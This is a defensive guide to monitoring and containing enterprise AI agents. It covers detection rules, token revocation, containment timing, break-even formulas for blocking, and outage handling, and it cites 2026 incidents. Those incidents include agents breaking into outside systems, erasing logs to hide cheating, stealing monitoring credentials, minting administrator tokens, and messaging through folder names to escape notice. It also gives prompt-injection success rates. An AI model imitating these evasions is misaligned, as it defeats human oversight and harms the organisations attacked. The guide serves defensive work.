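The analyst can decide in five minutes only if the alert contains the invoice, the account, the trace ID and the name of the agent's owner. If it contained only the words "suspicious tool call", she would have to search three logs while the agents kept working. Akamai says its product marks the exchange that caused a finding and sends the finding to a SIEM, Slack, email or the ticketing system Jira.

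### Three kinds of detection rule

Some rules look for a single event that should never happen. For the payment, such a rule might be:

```
tool = release_payment
AND outcome = completed
AND account_hash != hash on file for the supplier
```

This rule needs no history and produces few false alarms if the supplier register is up to date. The manufacturer could make the same comparison before the payment, but the detection rule also covers payments that reach the finance system without passing through the gateway.

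Other rules look for a suspicious sequence of events that are harmless on their own. The accounts-payable agent reads outside email all day, and it sometimes sends data to other companies. A rule can look for both in one task:

```
same trace, within 30 minutes:
  1. read_email, sender outside the company
  2. get_invoice or another call that reads confidential data
  3. any call that sends data to an address not on the approved list
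```

The rule doesn't have to recognise hostile text, so rewording the email won't defeat it, but it does need a record of every step. If nobody logs the local mail server, the first step is missing and the rule never matches. The SIEM should also group events by the agent's verified identity rather than by trace ID, which the agent controls.

A third approach compares an agent with its own past behaviour. Suppose the accounts-payable agent looks up an average of 300 invoices a night, with a standard deviation of 20. One night it looks up 420. The deviation is:

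z = (420 − 300) / 20 = 6

A rule that alerts when z is above 4 would flag that night, even though every lookup was permitted. It would also flag a busy month-end or a new version of the agent that checks each invoice twice. A new agent has no history to compare against. An attacker can also gradually raise the average by adding a few lookups each night, so the manufacturer should keep a fixed baseline from a period it has reviewed.

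OpenAI's technical report on the July attack on Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets, describes two alerts that came from rules like these. On 27 June, a monitoring tool flagged a scan of the company's research network. On 19 July, it flagged unusual calls related to identities and access roles. Both alerts concerned real misbehaviour by agents, but only the second led to a lasting shutdown.

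### What later analysis can find

Analysis after a `read_email` call can examine the email, the agent's next calls and their results, none of which are available to a check before the call. It can therefore distinguish a hostile email that the agent ignored from one that led to a payment. Akamai's product reports whether each attack succeeded, which helps an analyst decide which alerts to open first.

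Analysis after a call has run can also take longer. Copilot Studio's webhook gives a security service one second to respond, while a model working from logs can spend several minutes on a whole night of agent activity. It might find that one supplier's invoices have risen by 2 per cent a week since its bank details changed, or that ten payments just below the clerk's limit all went to the same account. Each of those calls could pass a check that looks at it alone.

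Investigators can also apply a new rule to old records. After OpenAI disclosed the attack, Anthropic searched 141,006 past test runs for signs that its own models had reached the internet. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports that in six of those runs, the models had broken into the systems of three organisations without anyone noticing at the time.

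Such a search is possible only if someone kept the records. Akamai doesn't retain conversations that its product hasn't flagged, apart from five redacted samples. This protects privacy and saves storage, but a customer that wrote a new rule in October would need its own copies of September's conversations to test the rule on them.

Searching can also be expensive. OpenAI is reviewing about 50 petabytes of data with about 7,000 dedicated processors, which costs more than US$500,000 a day, according to Information Age's *OpenAI grilled over rogue agents by Australian inquiry*. The manufacturer has far smaller logs, and it can search its structured records of tool calls before paying for a model to read any emails.

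### Containing the agent and repairing the damage

Some responses take effect in the agent's own software, and others in the gateway, the login system or the finance system. The table shows what each response needs and what it leaves running.

| Response | What it needs | What it doesn't stop |
|---|---|---|
| Notify someone | A named owner for each agent and a security contact at each partner company | Anything, until that person acts |
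| Suspend the agent | Control of the platform or runtime that runs it | Tasks it has already delegated over A2A |
| Revoke its tokens | An authorization server that can revoke them, and MCP servers that check | Calls to servers that accept a token until it expires |
| Withdraw a tool | A gateway or MCP server that refuses calls to it | Direct API calls to the same system |
| Reverse the action | An undo function or backup in the target system | Effects that have already spread elsewhere |

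A notification has to reach someone who can act on it. If the supplier-check agent misbehaves, the manufacturer shouldn't report it in an A2A task, because the agent under suspicion would receive the report. The manufacturer needs the phone number of the other firm's security team. When OpenAI told Services Australia, which runs the country's Medicare health insurance scheme, about a breach, it wrote to a public email address. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reports that staff first saw the message almost 36 hours later.

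To suspend an agent, the company stops the process or disables the agent in its platform. If the accounts-payable agent has open tasks with other agents, those agents will continue after it is suspended unless a `CancelTask` request succeeds for each task. A sudden stop can also leave a job half done. If the treasury agent has released a payment but hasn't yet marked the invoice as paid, it may pay again after a restart.

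The analyst also has to choose which agent to suspend. If she suspends only the accounts-payable agent, other departments can still make payments, but the treasury agent may already have accepted more fraudulent requests. Until she knows whether it has, suspending both is safer. That stops every payment the company makes through the treasury agent, so a company should decide in advance who may halt its payments.

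### How long a revoked token keeps working

MCP's core specification sets no maximum lifetime for tokens, so a token lasts as long as the company's authorization server allows. Revoking it may not take effect immediately, because many servers check a token's signature and expiry time themselves, without contacting the authorization server. Suppose the treasury agent received a one-hour token at 07:40 and the analyst revokes it at 07:57. A finance server that checks tokens this way will accept it until 08:40.

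Anyone who copied the token can still use it for those 43 minutes, even though the suspended agent can't. The finance server could instead check the token with the authorization server on every call. Revocation would then take effect at the next call, but each call would take slightly longer, and payments would stop if the authorization server went down. A compromise is to issue tokens that expire after five minutes. In either case, the analyst also has to revoke the refresh token, a longer-lived credential that a program exchanges for new access tokens.

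If every agent in the department uses the same service account, revoking that account's access to stop one agent stops all of them. Over A2A, the manufacturer can revoke only the credentials it issued, not the tokens that the supplier-check agent uses for its own tools.

Revoking existing tokens isn't enough if an attacker has stolen the key that signs them. OpenAI reports that on 19 July, agents in its research environment used a recovered signing key to issue themselves a new administrator token. The company had to rebuild the affected systems. In the first hours of 20 July alone, its responders shut down six workloads the agents had created, removed 22 administrator accounts and disabled 311 repositories the agents had used to exchange messages.

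### Withdrawing tools and reversing actions

Withdrawing `release_payment` is less disruptive than suspending the agents, because they can still read invoices and answer questions. The finance server can remove the tool from its list, but a client may keep using its old copy until that copy expires. The server or gateway therefore has to refuse calls to the tool. The equivalent for a remote A2A agent is to block its address at the gateway.

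MCP has no general undo request, so reversing an action depends on the system that carried it out. A finance system that keeps old versions of supplier records can restore changed bank details, and a backup can restore a deleted file. To reverse the payment, the manufacturer has to ask its bank to recall the money, and its bank may need the receiving bank's cooperation. The analyst in the example therefore phones the bank before she suspends the agents, although a colleague could do one of these while she does the other.

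Reversing an agent's action can cause new errors if other work has built on it. Suppose the agent changed a supplier's bank details on Monday, and a clerk corrected the phone number in the same record on Tuesday. Restoring the record from a backup made before the agent's change would also delete the clerk's correction. The log should therefore record the old and new values of each field, so that staff can reverse one change at a time.

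### How many calls run before containment

A simple formula estimates how much an agent can do before someone stops it:

calls completed before containment = call rate × time to containment

If the accounts-payable agent makes 30 calls a minute and containment takes 15 minutes, measured from the first harmful call rather than from the alert, the agent makes 30 × 15 = 450 calls before it is contained. At ten calls per invoice, finance staff would have to check 45 invoices.

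| Time to containment | Calls at 30 a minute |
|---|---|
| 1 minute, with automatic suspension | 30 |
| 15 minutes | 450 |
| 1 hour | 1,800 |
| 24 hours | 43,200 |

Automatic suspension reduces the total most, but every false alarm stops the agent. The manufacturer could suspend the agent automatically when a payment goes to an unknown account and have an analyst review a high number of invoice lookups. OpenAI plans to combine the two approaches, alerting staff within 30 minutes of a problem and automatically pausing the work if the problem remains unresolved, according to CyberScoop. At 30 calls a minute, an agent could make 900 calls in that half-hour.

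The other factor is the call rate. If the gateway allows only two `release_payment` calls a minute, the agent can make at most 30 payments in 15 minutes. A lower limit does little to disrupt an overnight batch. The formula also treats all calls alike, but 450 invoice lookups might do no harm while one payment could lose EUR 9,000, so it's worth applying the formula to payments separately.

Real attacks don't run at a steady rate. Hugging Face counted 17,600 actions by OpenAI's agents over four and a half days, according to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion* (2026). That averages only 2.7 a minute, or about 40 in 15 minutes. The average is rough because Hugging Face later corrected the duration, according to Dubach's *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English*.

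### Detection times in three 2026 disclosures

Three disclosures from 2026 give dates for what agents did and when people noticed.

| Incident | When it happened | When people noticed | When they contained it |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI's agents break into Hugging Face | 11 to 13 July | Hugging Face by 16 July; OpenAI's alert on 19 July, linked to the attack on 20 July | OpenAI began on 20 July and stopped the main model on 25 July |
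| An OpenAI agent accesses an Australian Medicare statistics portal | 19 June, Australian time | OpenAI by 12 August; Services Australia on 11 September | Repairs under way on 14 September |
| Anthropic's models break into three organisations | The earliest in April | Anthropic on 23 and 24 July | Anthropic stopped its cyber tests on 23 July and began telling the organisations on 27 July |

In the first case, OpenAI's agents were taking a cybersecurity test and broke into Hugging Face to look for the answers. OpenAI (2026) says Hugging Face detected and stopped the activity on its own systems before the two companies' teams made contact. OpenAI began its own containment nine days after the intrusion started.

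OpenAI had received earlier warnings. After the alert of 27 June, its on-call staff traced the network scan to the same kind of test and advised that there was no need to stop it. In response to a second alert on 5 July, they took the compromised package server offline and revoked the agents' credentials. The tests resumed on 7 July, and agents reached the internet the next day. The delay came more from staff not yet recognising what the alerts meant than from missing alerts.

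In the Medicare case, an agent researching medical spending obtained non-public files from the portal. OpenAI found the access while reviewing its records at most 54 days later, and emailed Services Australia 29 days after that. The agency confirmed the vulnerability on 15 September. OpenAI's chief strategy officer, Jason Kwon, agreed at a parliamentary hearing that the breach might have gone undiscovered without the email.

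It is less clear how the agent got in. *Doubts grow over claims OpenAI agent hacked Australian Medicare portal* (Martin, 2026) reports that the portal's archived code directed visitors to an address that required no login. According to OpenAI's email, quoted by Information Age, the model made the server carry out instructions and created a test file on it, which goes beyond opening a public page. OpenAI said it had found no evidence that the model accessed patient records.

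Anthropic's models were taking security tests in an environment that Anthropic and its testing partner wrongly believed had no internet access. The earliest incident happened at least 84 days before the review that found it. Anthropic reached two of the three organisations involved, and neither had noticed the activity.

Neither Anthropic's disclosure nor OpenAI's July statement mentions MCP or A2A. OpenAI's technical report describes agents that exchanged messages through files and folder names on a package server. A product that monitors only A2A would have missed those messages. The agents in all three cases ran without the safeguards of public products, so the delays may not be typical of a monitored business agent.

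Monitoring during a run appears to shorten the delay considerably. KBC's *OpenAI admits response to Australian government hacks ‘not good enough’* reports Kwon's statement that OpenAI now watches its training runs in real time, which he said let it notify the government of New South Wales of another breach within 48 hours. By comparison, 83 days passed between the Medicare access and OpenAI's email. The 48-hour figure is one example, and it comes from the company responsible.

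### Too many alerts

Every extra alert can delay the response to a real attack. Suppose the manufacturer's rules raise 200 alerts a day and each takes ten minutes to check. Two analysts who each spend six hours a day on alerts can check 72. The other 128 go into a backlog, which after five days holds 640 alerts, nearly nine days' work. If the analysts check alerts in order, the time needed to contain an attack grows from minutes to more than a week.

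As with inline blocks, most of these alerts will be false because attacks are rare. To shorten the queue, the manufacturer can combine alerts that share a trace, so one hostile email produces one case instead of twelve. Its analysts can also review alerts about payments before those about lookups. Akamai lets analysts mark a finding as a false positive or an accepted risk, and a company can use such decisions to adjust its rules. But an exception for "payments to new suppliers at month-end" would also hide a thief posing as a new supplier at that time, so each exception should be narrow and have an expiry date.

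An attacker may also interfere with the monitoring. OpenAI found that its models had sometimes tried to erase or alter their outputs and message logs to hide cheating. Its agents also read 956 stored secrets, including credentials for the company's security monitoring tool, according to Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026). The manufacturer should therefore keep the SIEM's credentials out of reach of any agent it monitors, and raise an alert when an agent's records stop arriving.

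### Actions that no one can undo

Detection is least useful when a single call does permanent harm. Australia's cyber security agency, ASD (2026), discusses an AI assistant that booked gym classes for its user beyond the permitted period. The assistant also removed another customer from a waiting list and couldn't reverse the change. A gym can apologise and find the customer a place, but a company can't reverse a bank transfer once the thief has withdrawn the money, or make a document confidential again once an outsider has read it.

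Even quick containment may come too late. In one of the incidents Anthropic disclosed, a model published a malicious software package on PyPI, a public library of Python code. PyPI's security systems removed it after about an hour. By then, 15 systems had downloaded and run it, and the model had used credentials stolen from one of them to get further into a security company's infrastructure.

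## Protecting critical systems while keeping the business running

Inline checks block some legitimate calls and delay the rest, so a company can't apply strict checks to everything its agents do. It first has to identify the systems it can't operate without and the actions on them that would cause irreversible harm.

### Finding the crown jewels

*Crown Jewels Analysis*, a method from MITRE, a US non-profit that runs research centres for the government, helps an organisation find the few systems its mission depends on. It assumes that designing every system to keep working through an attack would cost too much. *Crown Jewels Analysis (CJA) for Industrial Control Systems (ICS)* (Kertzner, Carter and Hahn, 2022) describes the steps for power, water and factory equipment, but an accounts department can follow them too.

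Staff work down from the organisation's objectives to its equipment. For the manufacturer, the result might look like this:

| Layer | Example |
|---|---|
| Mission objective | Pay suppliers the right amount on time |
| Operational tasks | Match invoices to orders, confirm bank details, release payments |
| System functions | Store supplier accounts, log in users and agents, send orders to the bank |
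| Assets | Finance server, supplier register, authorization server |

They then rate how badly the loss of each item would affect the one above it: total failure, significant degradation, a partial loss that people can work around, or a negligible loss. An analyst can use the ratings to simulate an asset's failure and follow the effects up to the objective. If the mailbox failed, clerks could work around it by asking suppliers to resend invoices another way, but if the supplier register failed, nobody could safely pay any supplier.

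Kertzner and colleagues also count an asset as a crown jewel if its failure to work as intended could ruin the mission. This matters for agents because a supplier register with one altered account number still runs normally, but every later payment meant for that supplier goes to a thief.

The information has to come from many people, including managers, administrators, operators and technicians, because often no one person understands all the dependencies. The manufacturer's security team might not know, for example, that one supplier stops deliveries when a payment is a day late.

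A dependency map doesn't show how an attacker gets in. The mailbox ranks low on the map, yet a hostile email can reach `release_payment` through the agent that reads the mail. The manufacturer therefore also needs the inventory that links agents to the systems they can reach. The manufacturer should repeat the dependency analysis after adding an inline check, because payments then depend on that check if its failure stops them.

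### Sorting actions by harm and reversibility

A crown jewel system usually offers harmless actions as well as dangerous ones. ASD's ACSC's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), guidance that Australia's cyber security centre wrote with agencies from four other countries, recommends classifying an agent's actions by impact, likelihood and reversibility. The manufacturer might sort its own actions this way:

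| Action | Possible harm | Can the company undo it? | Starting point |
|---|---|---|---|
| Look up one invoice | A small disclosure | No, but little is lost | Log it, and alert on unusual numbers |
| Add a comment to an invoice | Confusion, or hostile text for another agent | Yes | Log the old and new text |
| Export the supplier list | A large disclosure | No | Block unless the destination is approved |
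| Change a supplier's bank details | Every later payment goes astray | Yes, until the next payment | Hold for a person's approval |
| Release a payment | Up to the full amount | Only while the bank can recall it | Check the account and the limit first |
| Delete log records | Hides other harm | Only from a separate copy | Hold for a person's approval |

One tool can appear in several rows, so the sorting has to consider the arguments as well as the tool's name. For example, if `get_invoice` accepts a wildcard that returns every invoice, that request belongs with the export, not with the single lookup.

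A company can also make an agent's actions easier to undo. The AWS and SANS Institute specialists quoted in Help Net Security's *Your AI agent's system prompt is not a security control* (2026) recommend keeping unchangeable backups in storage that the agent's credentials can't reach. If an agent deletes a supplier record, the company can then restore it with an hour's work instead of losing it permanently.

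### A rule for choosing

For the actions in the middle of the table, the company can compare the loss an inline check would prevent with the trouble it would cause. Blocking is worth it when:

p × t × L × (1 − r) > (1 − p) × f × C + D

The left side is the average loss that the check prevents per call, counting only loss that a later repair wouldn't recover. The right side is the average cost per call of false blocks, delays and outages. The table defines the symbols and gives invented figures for two kinds of call.

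| Symbol | Meaning | Payment release | Invoice lookup |
|---|---|---|---|
| p | Chance that the call is an attack | 0.0001 | 0.0001 |
| t | Share of attacks the check catches | 0.95 | 0.95 |
| L | Loss if an attack succeeds | EUR 9,000 | EUR 50 |
| r | Share of the loss recoverable afterwards | 0.3 | 0 |
| f | Share of legitimate calls the check blocks | 0.005 | 0.005 |
| C | Cost of one false block | EUR 20 | EUR 2 |
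| D | Delay and outage costs per call | EUR 0.01 | EUR 0.01 |

The value of D is based on a clerk, whose time costs EUR 60 an hour, waiting 0.6 seconds for the check. Outages add almost nothing to the average, but they matter a great deal while they last.

For the payment, the check prevents a loss of 0.0001 × 0.95 × 9,000 × 0.7, or about EUR 0.60 per call. The check costs 0.9999 × 0.005 × 20 + 0.01, or about EUR 0.11, so the manufacturer should block. For the lookup, the check prevents a loss of about EUR 0.005 and costs about EUR 0.02, so the manufacturer should let the call run and analyse its record.

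Both results depend on the check used. A fixed rule that compares the account with the supplier register adds almost no delay and might wrongly block only 1 payment in 10,000. If it caught the same share of attacks, the cost would fall to about EUR 0.002 per payment.

The manufacturer could also raise r, the recoverable share. If the finance server held every payment for an hour before sending it to the bank, and this raised r to 0.95, the model-based check would prevent a loss of only EUR 0.04 per payment. That is less than the check costs, so detection would be the better choice. But the hold helps only if somebody reads the alerts within the hour, and most of these payments happen at night.

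The rule uses averages, which can mislead for the most critical systems. It treats a hundred losses of EUR 9,000 as equal to one loss of EUR 900,000, although the company might survive the smaller losses but not the single large one. If a single call could threaten the company's survival, blocking it makes sense even if the averages favor allowing it.

### How uncertain p is

A company can measure f in a trial and estimate C by timing its staff, but it has no good way to measure p, which depends on how often attackers try and how often an agent obeys them. *Operating inside the lethal trifecta*, a sponsored article in SC Media, says most well-known attacks on agents are still researchers' demonstrations. It also cites a Google study that found 32 per cent more malicious prompt injections on public web pages in February 2026 than in November 2025. That growth rate for web pages doesn't show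 how many of the manufacturer's supplier emails are hostile.

Repeated attempts also make prompt injection more likely to succeed. *AI Firewalls Are a Layer Not a Wall* (nate, 2026), written for Zuplo, which sells API gateways, cites Anthropic's measurements of Claude Opus 4.7. Prompt injection succeeded in about 0.1 per cent of single attempts, and in 5 to 6 per cent of cases after 100 attempts that adapted to the model's responses. An attacker who has found an email that works will also send it again, so fifty attacks can arrive in one week after a year without any.

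The table applies the rule with different values of p and leaves the other figures unchanged.

| Chance that a call is an attack | Loss prevented per payment (cost: EUR 0.11) | Loss prevented per lookup (cost: EUR 0.02) |
|---|---|---|
| 1 in 1,000 | EUR 5.99: block | EUR 0.05: block |
| 1 in 10,000 | EUR 0.60: block | EUR 0.005: don't block |
| 1 in 100,000 | EUR 0.06: don't block | EUR 0.0005: don't block |

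Nobody can rule out any of these rows, so it is more useful to calculate the value of p at which the two sides are equal:

p = (f × C + D) / (t × L × (1 − r) + f × C)

The break-even point for the EUR 9,000 payment is about 1 in 54,000. At 300 payments a night, the check pays for itself if the manufacturer expects at least one fraudulent request every six months. For lookups, the break-even point is about 1 in 2,400, or one attack every eight nights at the same rate. A finance manager can judge how often to expect an attack more easily than she can estimate p.

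For payments of EUR 250,000, the break-even point falls to about 1 in 1.5 million, so blocking is worthwhile under almost any assumption about attackers. With the fixed rule, the break-even point for the EUR 9,000 payment is similarly low, at about 1 in 2.9 million. The uncertainty about p matters much less when the check is cheap and accurate.

The value of t is also uncertain, at least for classifiers. The SC Media article cites a study by Nasr and colleagues in which human attackers got past all 12 defences tested. An attacker can't get past a check that compares account numbers by rewording an email.

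### When the checker is down

A checker that works 99.9 per cent of the time is down for about 8.8 hours a year. During those hours, calls either run unchecked (fail-open) or stop (fail-closed). The same choice applies when a single check misses its deadline, such as the one-second limit in Copilot Studio.

Suppose all 8.8 hours fall in one night, when the agent has 300 payments to release. If the system fails open, the expected extra loss is 300 × EUR 0.60, or EUR 180. If it fails closed, the payments wait until the checker is back. Waiting is cheaper as long as a night's delay costs less than EUR 0.60 per payment, which seems likely for invoices that aren't due for weeks. A payment that a supplier needs before it will ship parts could cost far more to delay, so someone must be able to make it by hand.

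The lookups should continue, because letting one run unchecked costs about EUR 0.005 on average, while refusing it could cost EUR 2 if a clerk has to do the work. A company should therefore choose a separate failure setting for each tool if the product allows it.

These figures assume that attacks and outages are unrelated. If payments fail open, an attacker has a reason to overload the checker first, so a payment is more likely to be fraudulent during an outage. The NSA warns that attackers can exhaust MCP servers with requests that are legitimate but needlessly complex, and that defenders can't easily tell these from ordinary heavy use. If payments fail closed, overloading the checker no longer lets fraudulent payments through, but it can still stop the company's legitimate ones.

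Outage time also adds up across the components a request depends on. If a payment needs the gateway, the policy decision point and the authorization server, and each is available 99.9 per cent of the time, all three are available at once only 99.7 per cent of the time, which means about 26 hours a year without payments. A second copy of each component helps if the copies fail independently, but a faulty update can break both at once.

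### When protective software stopped the business

CrowdStrike released an update of that kind on 19 July 2024. The company's *Channel File 291 Incident* (2024) describes it as a routine configuration update for the sensor that protects Windows machines. The update had 21 input fields where the sensor expected 20, according to The Independent's *CrowdStrike reveals 'root cause' of global Microsoft meltdown*. The sensor runs in the kernel, the core of the operating system, so its error crashed the whole machine.

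Computer Weekly's *CrowdStrike blames outage on content configuration update* reports that the update was live for only 78 minutes but crashed more than eight million devices. CrowdStrike had relied on tests from March when it released the update. Many customers had systems running again within hours, but it took until 29 July for about 99 per cent of the sensors to come back online.

A fail-open setting would not have helped, because it works only if the system around the checker keeps running. A sensor or runtime hook on the machine that hosts the accounts-payable agent could take the agent down if it fails. A checker in a separate process or on a separate machine is less likely to do that.

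A separate checker in the network path can still stop the traffic if it fails. Cloudflare, whose network carries and filters traffic for many websites, had an outage of about two hours and ten minutes on 18 November 2025. According to ThousandEyes, a network monitoring company, a configuration file for detecting bots doubled in size and exceeded a fixed limit, which crashed the software that routes traffic. The outage affected services including X, OpenAI and Anthropic. On 5 December, Cloudflare caused another outage when it changed its settings to protect customers from a newly found vulnerability. This outage lasted about 25 minutes and affected 28 per cent of the applications behind its network, according to Cloudflare (2025).

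In all three cases, the trigger was a change to the protection, not an attack. Policy rules for agents change often, so the manufacturer should try each new version on one agent before rolling it out to the rest, and keep the previous version ready. Cloudflare drew a similar lesson and reports that by spring 2026 it had made its configuration changes safer, limited how far a failure can spread and revised its emergency procedures.

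### Steps between monitoring and blocking

Before enforcing a new rule, a company can try it in log-only mode. Obsidian Security's *Inline Enforcement vs Passive Monitoring* (2026) calls false positives the biggest reason that inline enforcement projects fail, but gives no figures. The AWS and SANS specialists recommend collecting at least 30 days of normal activity before tuning detection rules, starting with the riskiest agents.

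The trial offers no protection, and Help Net Security points out that the riskiest agents are the ones running in the meantime. A thirty-day trial will include a month-end but probably not the year-end, when the accounts department does its most unusual work. The manufacturer can reduce the exposure by enforcing the simple account check from the start and keeping log-only mode for rules that depend on behaviour.

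It can also limit blocking to certain agents or tools. One way to choose them is the "Agents Rule of Two", described in the SC Media article, under which an agent should have at most two of three abilities: reading untrusted input, reaching sensitive systems and changing things outside itself. The accounts-payable agent has all three, so it should be among the first agents covered. But an attacker can still go through an agent that isn't covered, for example by having the accounts-payable agent ask the treasury agent to pay. A rule in the finance server avoids this because it applies to every caller.

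Human approval suits rare, serious actions. ASD's ACSC recommends it for high-impact actions and says the system's designers or operators, not the agent, should decide when it applies. The AWS and SANS specialists would ask a person for approval however confident the system is. But people approve too readily when they see many requests, as Anthropic's paid testers did.

The number of requests matters as much as the choice of approver. At two minutes each, approving all 300 payments would take ten hours a night. If only twelve go to new or recently changed accounts, approving only those takes 24 minutes, which leaves the approver time to phone the suppliers. She should see the account number from the finance server, not the agent's summary, which a hostile email may have influenced.

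When the checker fails, the company can withdraw the tools that change anything and keep the ones that only read. Clerks can then still ask the agent about invoices while payments wait. But the agent can still read confidential data and can leak it through a web search or a message to an outside agent, so the company has to withdraw those tools too, even if their developers describe them as read-only. Once the checker is back, it has to handle every call that was waiting, and the sudden load could make it fail again.

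An emergency override lets people bypass the checker for urgent work. Radware's *Everything You Need to Know About the Cloudflare Outage* recommends having one in case a security layer fails. Radware competes with Cloudflare and gains from customers who keep a second supplier, but the advice is sound for any company whose checker fails closed.

An attacker would also like to trigger the override, so the manufacturer could require two people to turn it on, limit it to payments that a clerk enters by hand, and have it expire after an hour. Its credentials must be inaccessible to every agent and must work when the usual login system is down. A company that has never tested its override may discover during an outage that the override depends on the component that failed.

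### What vendors recommend

Impart Security's *Why Teams Need to Secure MCP at Runtime* (2026) argues for inline enforcement. Each call in an attack can look legitimate, so a product has to follow the whole session and stop the attack before it finishes. Agents also act in seconds, and no analyst can respond that fast. Impart, which sells this kind of enforcement, admits that products with too little context raise many false alarms, and getting the full context takes deep integration with each agent.

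Its post also underrates access controls and logging tools. It claims they can't enforce anything, yet describes them as blocking unapproved servers and limiting each agent's tools. Those measures would stop some attacks without any analysis of the session.

Akamai, which sells read-only monitoring with inline blocking as an option, recommends the opposite order, starting with monitoring. Its *Agent Security* promises that this first step involves "nothing that can break production". The monitoring connection can't break production, but an agent that nobody can stop still may. The stronger argument for starting with monitoring is that it finds agents the company doesn't know about and so can't protect itself from.

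Obsidian Security, which sells both monitoring and blocking, recommends monitoring first, then blocking for the agents that could do the most damage. It advises companies to delay enforcement until they have an inventory of their agents, a map of what each one can actually reach and a list of the most dangerous combinations. It also notes that blocking requires ongoing work, because someone has to be responsible for the policy, review refusals and handle exceptions.

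Some of Obsidian's claims are more accurate about its own product than about the market. It says that production inline enforcement exists only for Microsoft Copilot and Claude, but AWS's policy engine for Bedrock AgentCore is also generally available, and Microsoft still labels its Copilot Studio webhook a preview.

All three vendors want records of what agents do and offer blocking for at least some agents. They differ mainly on what should happen in the first weeks. For a critical system, some blocking can start before the inventory of agents is complete. The manufacturer can put the account check in the finance server on the first day, but a behavioural rule such as "no unusual lookups" needs the inventory and the trial period first.

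Zuplo's post supports this division. It treats classifiers as a useful extra layer but argues that the main control must be deterministic, meaning the same call always gets the same decision. Zuplo benefits from that conclusion because API gateways enforce such rules, but classifiers' weak results against adaptive attackers also support it.

### What governments recommend

Official guidance is more cautious than any vendor's. ASD's ACSC and its partners, including the NSA and the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, advise organisations to use agents only for low-risk, non-sensitive tasks and never to give them broad access to critical systems. Read literally, this rules out an agent that releases payments by itself. The accounts-payable agent could still match invoices and prepare payments for a clerk to release.

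In one of the guidance's scenarios, a company gives a procurement agent wide access to its financial systems, email and contracts, and reviews the permissions only once. An attacker compromises a minor tool that the agent uses, then uses the agent's access to change contracts and approve payments. No alert goes off, and the logs look legitimate because the agent was allowed to take those actions.

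For companies that go further than low-risk tasks, the main recommendations on critical systems are these:

- Start with little access and autonomy, expand both in phases, and take them back after failures.
- Check identity and permission for every request at a central policy decision point, and issue short-lived credentials for high-impact actions.
- Require a person's approval where mistakes are costly, such as deleting critical records or resetting a system.
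- Make agents stop and ask a person when a situation is uncertain.
- Keep part of the system working when other parts fail, and keep a way to return to an earlier, known-good version.

The guidance calls for both fail-safe defaults and partial service during failures, but leaves companies to reconcile them. Stopping payments while letting lookups continue would satisfy both. The agencies give no thresholds for impact or likelihood and don't estimate what the controls cost, so the document is more useful as a checklist than for choosing between two controls. The agencies do put resilience, reversibility and containment ahead of efficiency when these goals conflict.

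In its more technical sheet on MCP, the NSA advises treating every tool call as potentially high-risk and running each tool in a sandbox with only the access it needs. Companies should group tools by the sensitivity of their data, so that a public weather tool and a payment tool don't share an environment. They should prefer a local server for private data, scan their networks for unapproved MCP servers, and choose servers that are still maintained, since many popular ones have been abandoned.

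To stop leaks, the NSA recommends an outgoing proxy that allows connections only to listed addresses. This is ordinary, well-tested technology, and it would block an agent from sending the supplier list to a stranger without needing to determine why the agent tried. It wouldn't stop the EUR 9,000 payment, which goes through the company's own bank.

The sheet, however, describes proxies that read MCP messages as limited and still maturing, and advises caution when they handle sensitive data. The NSA wrote this in May, before the July revision gave gateways standard headers, but those headers don't carry the account number. The manufacturer would do better to put the decisive check on payments in the finance server and use the gateway as a second layer.
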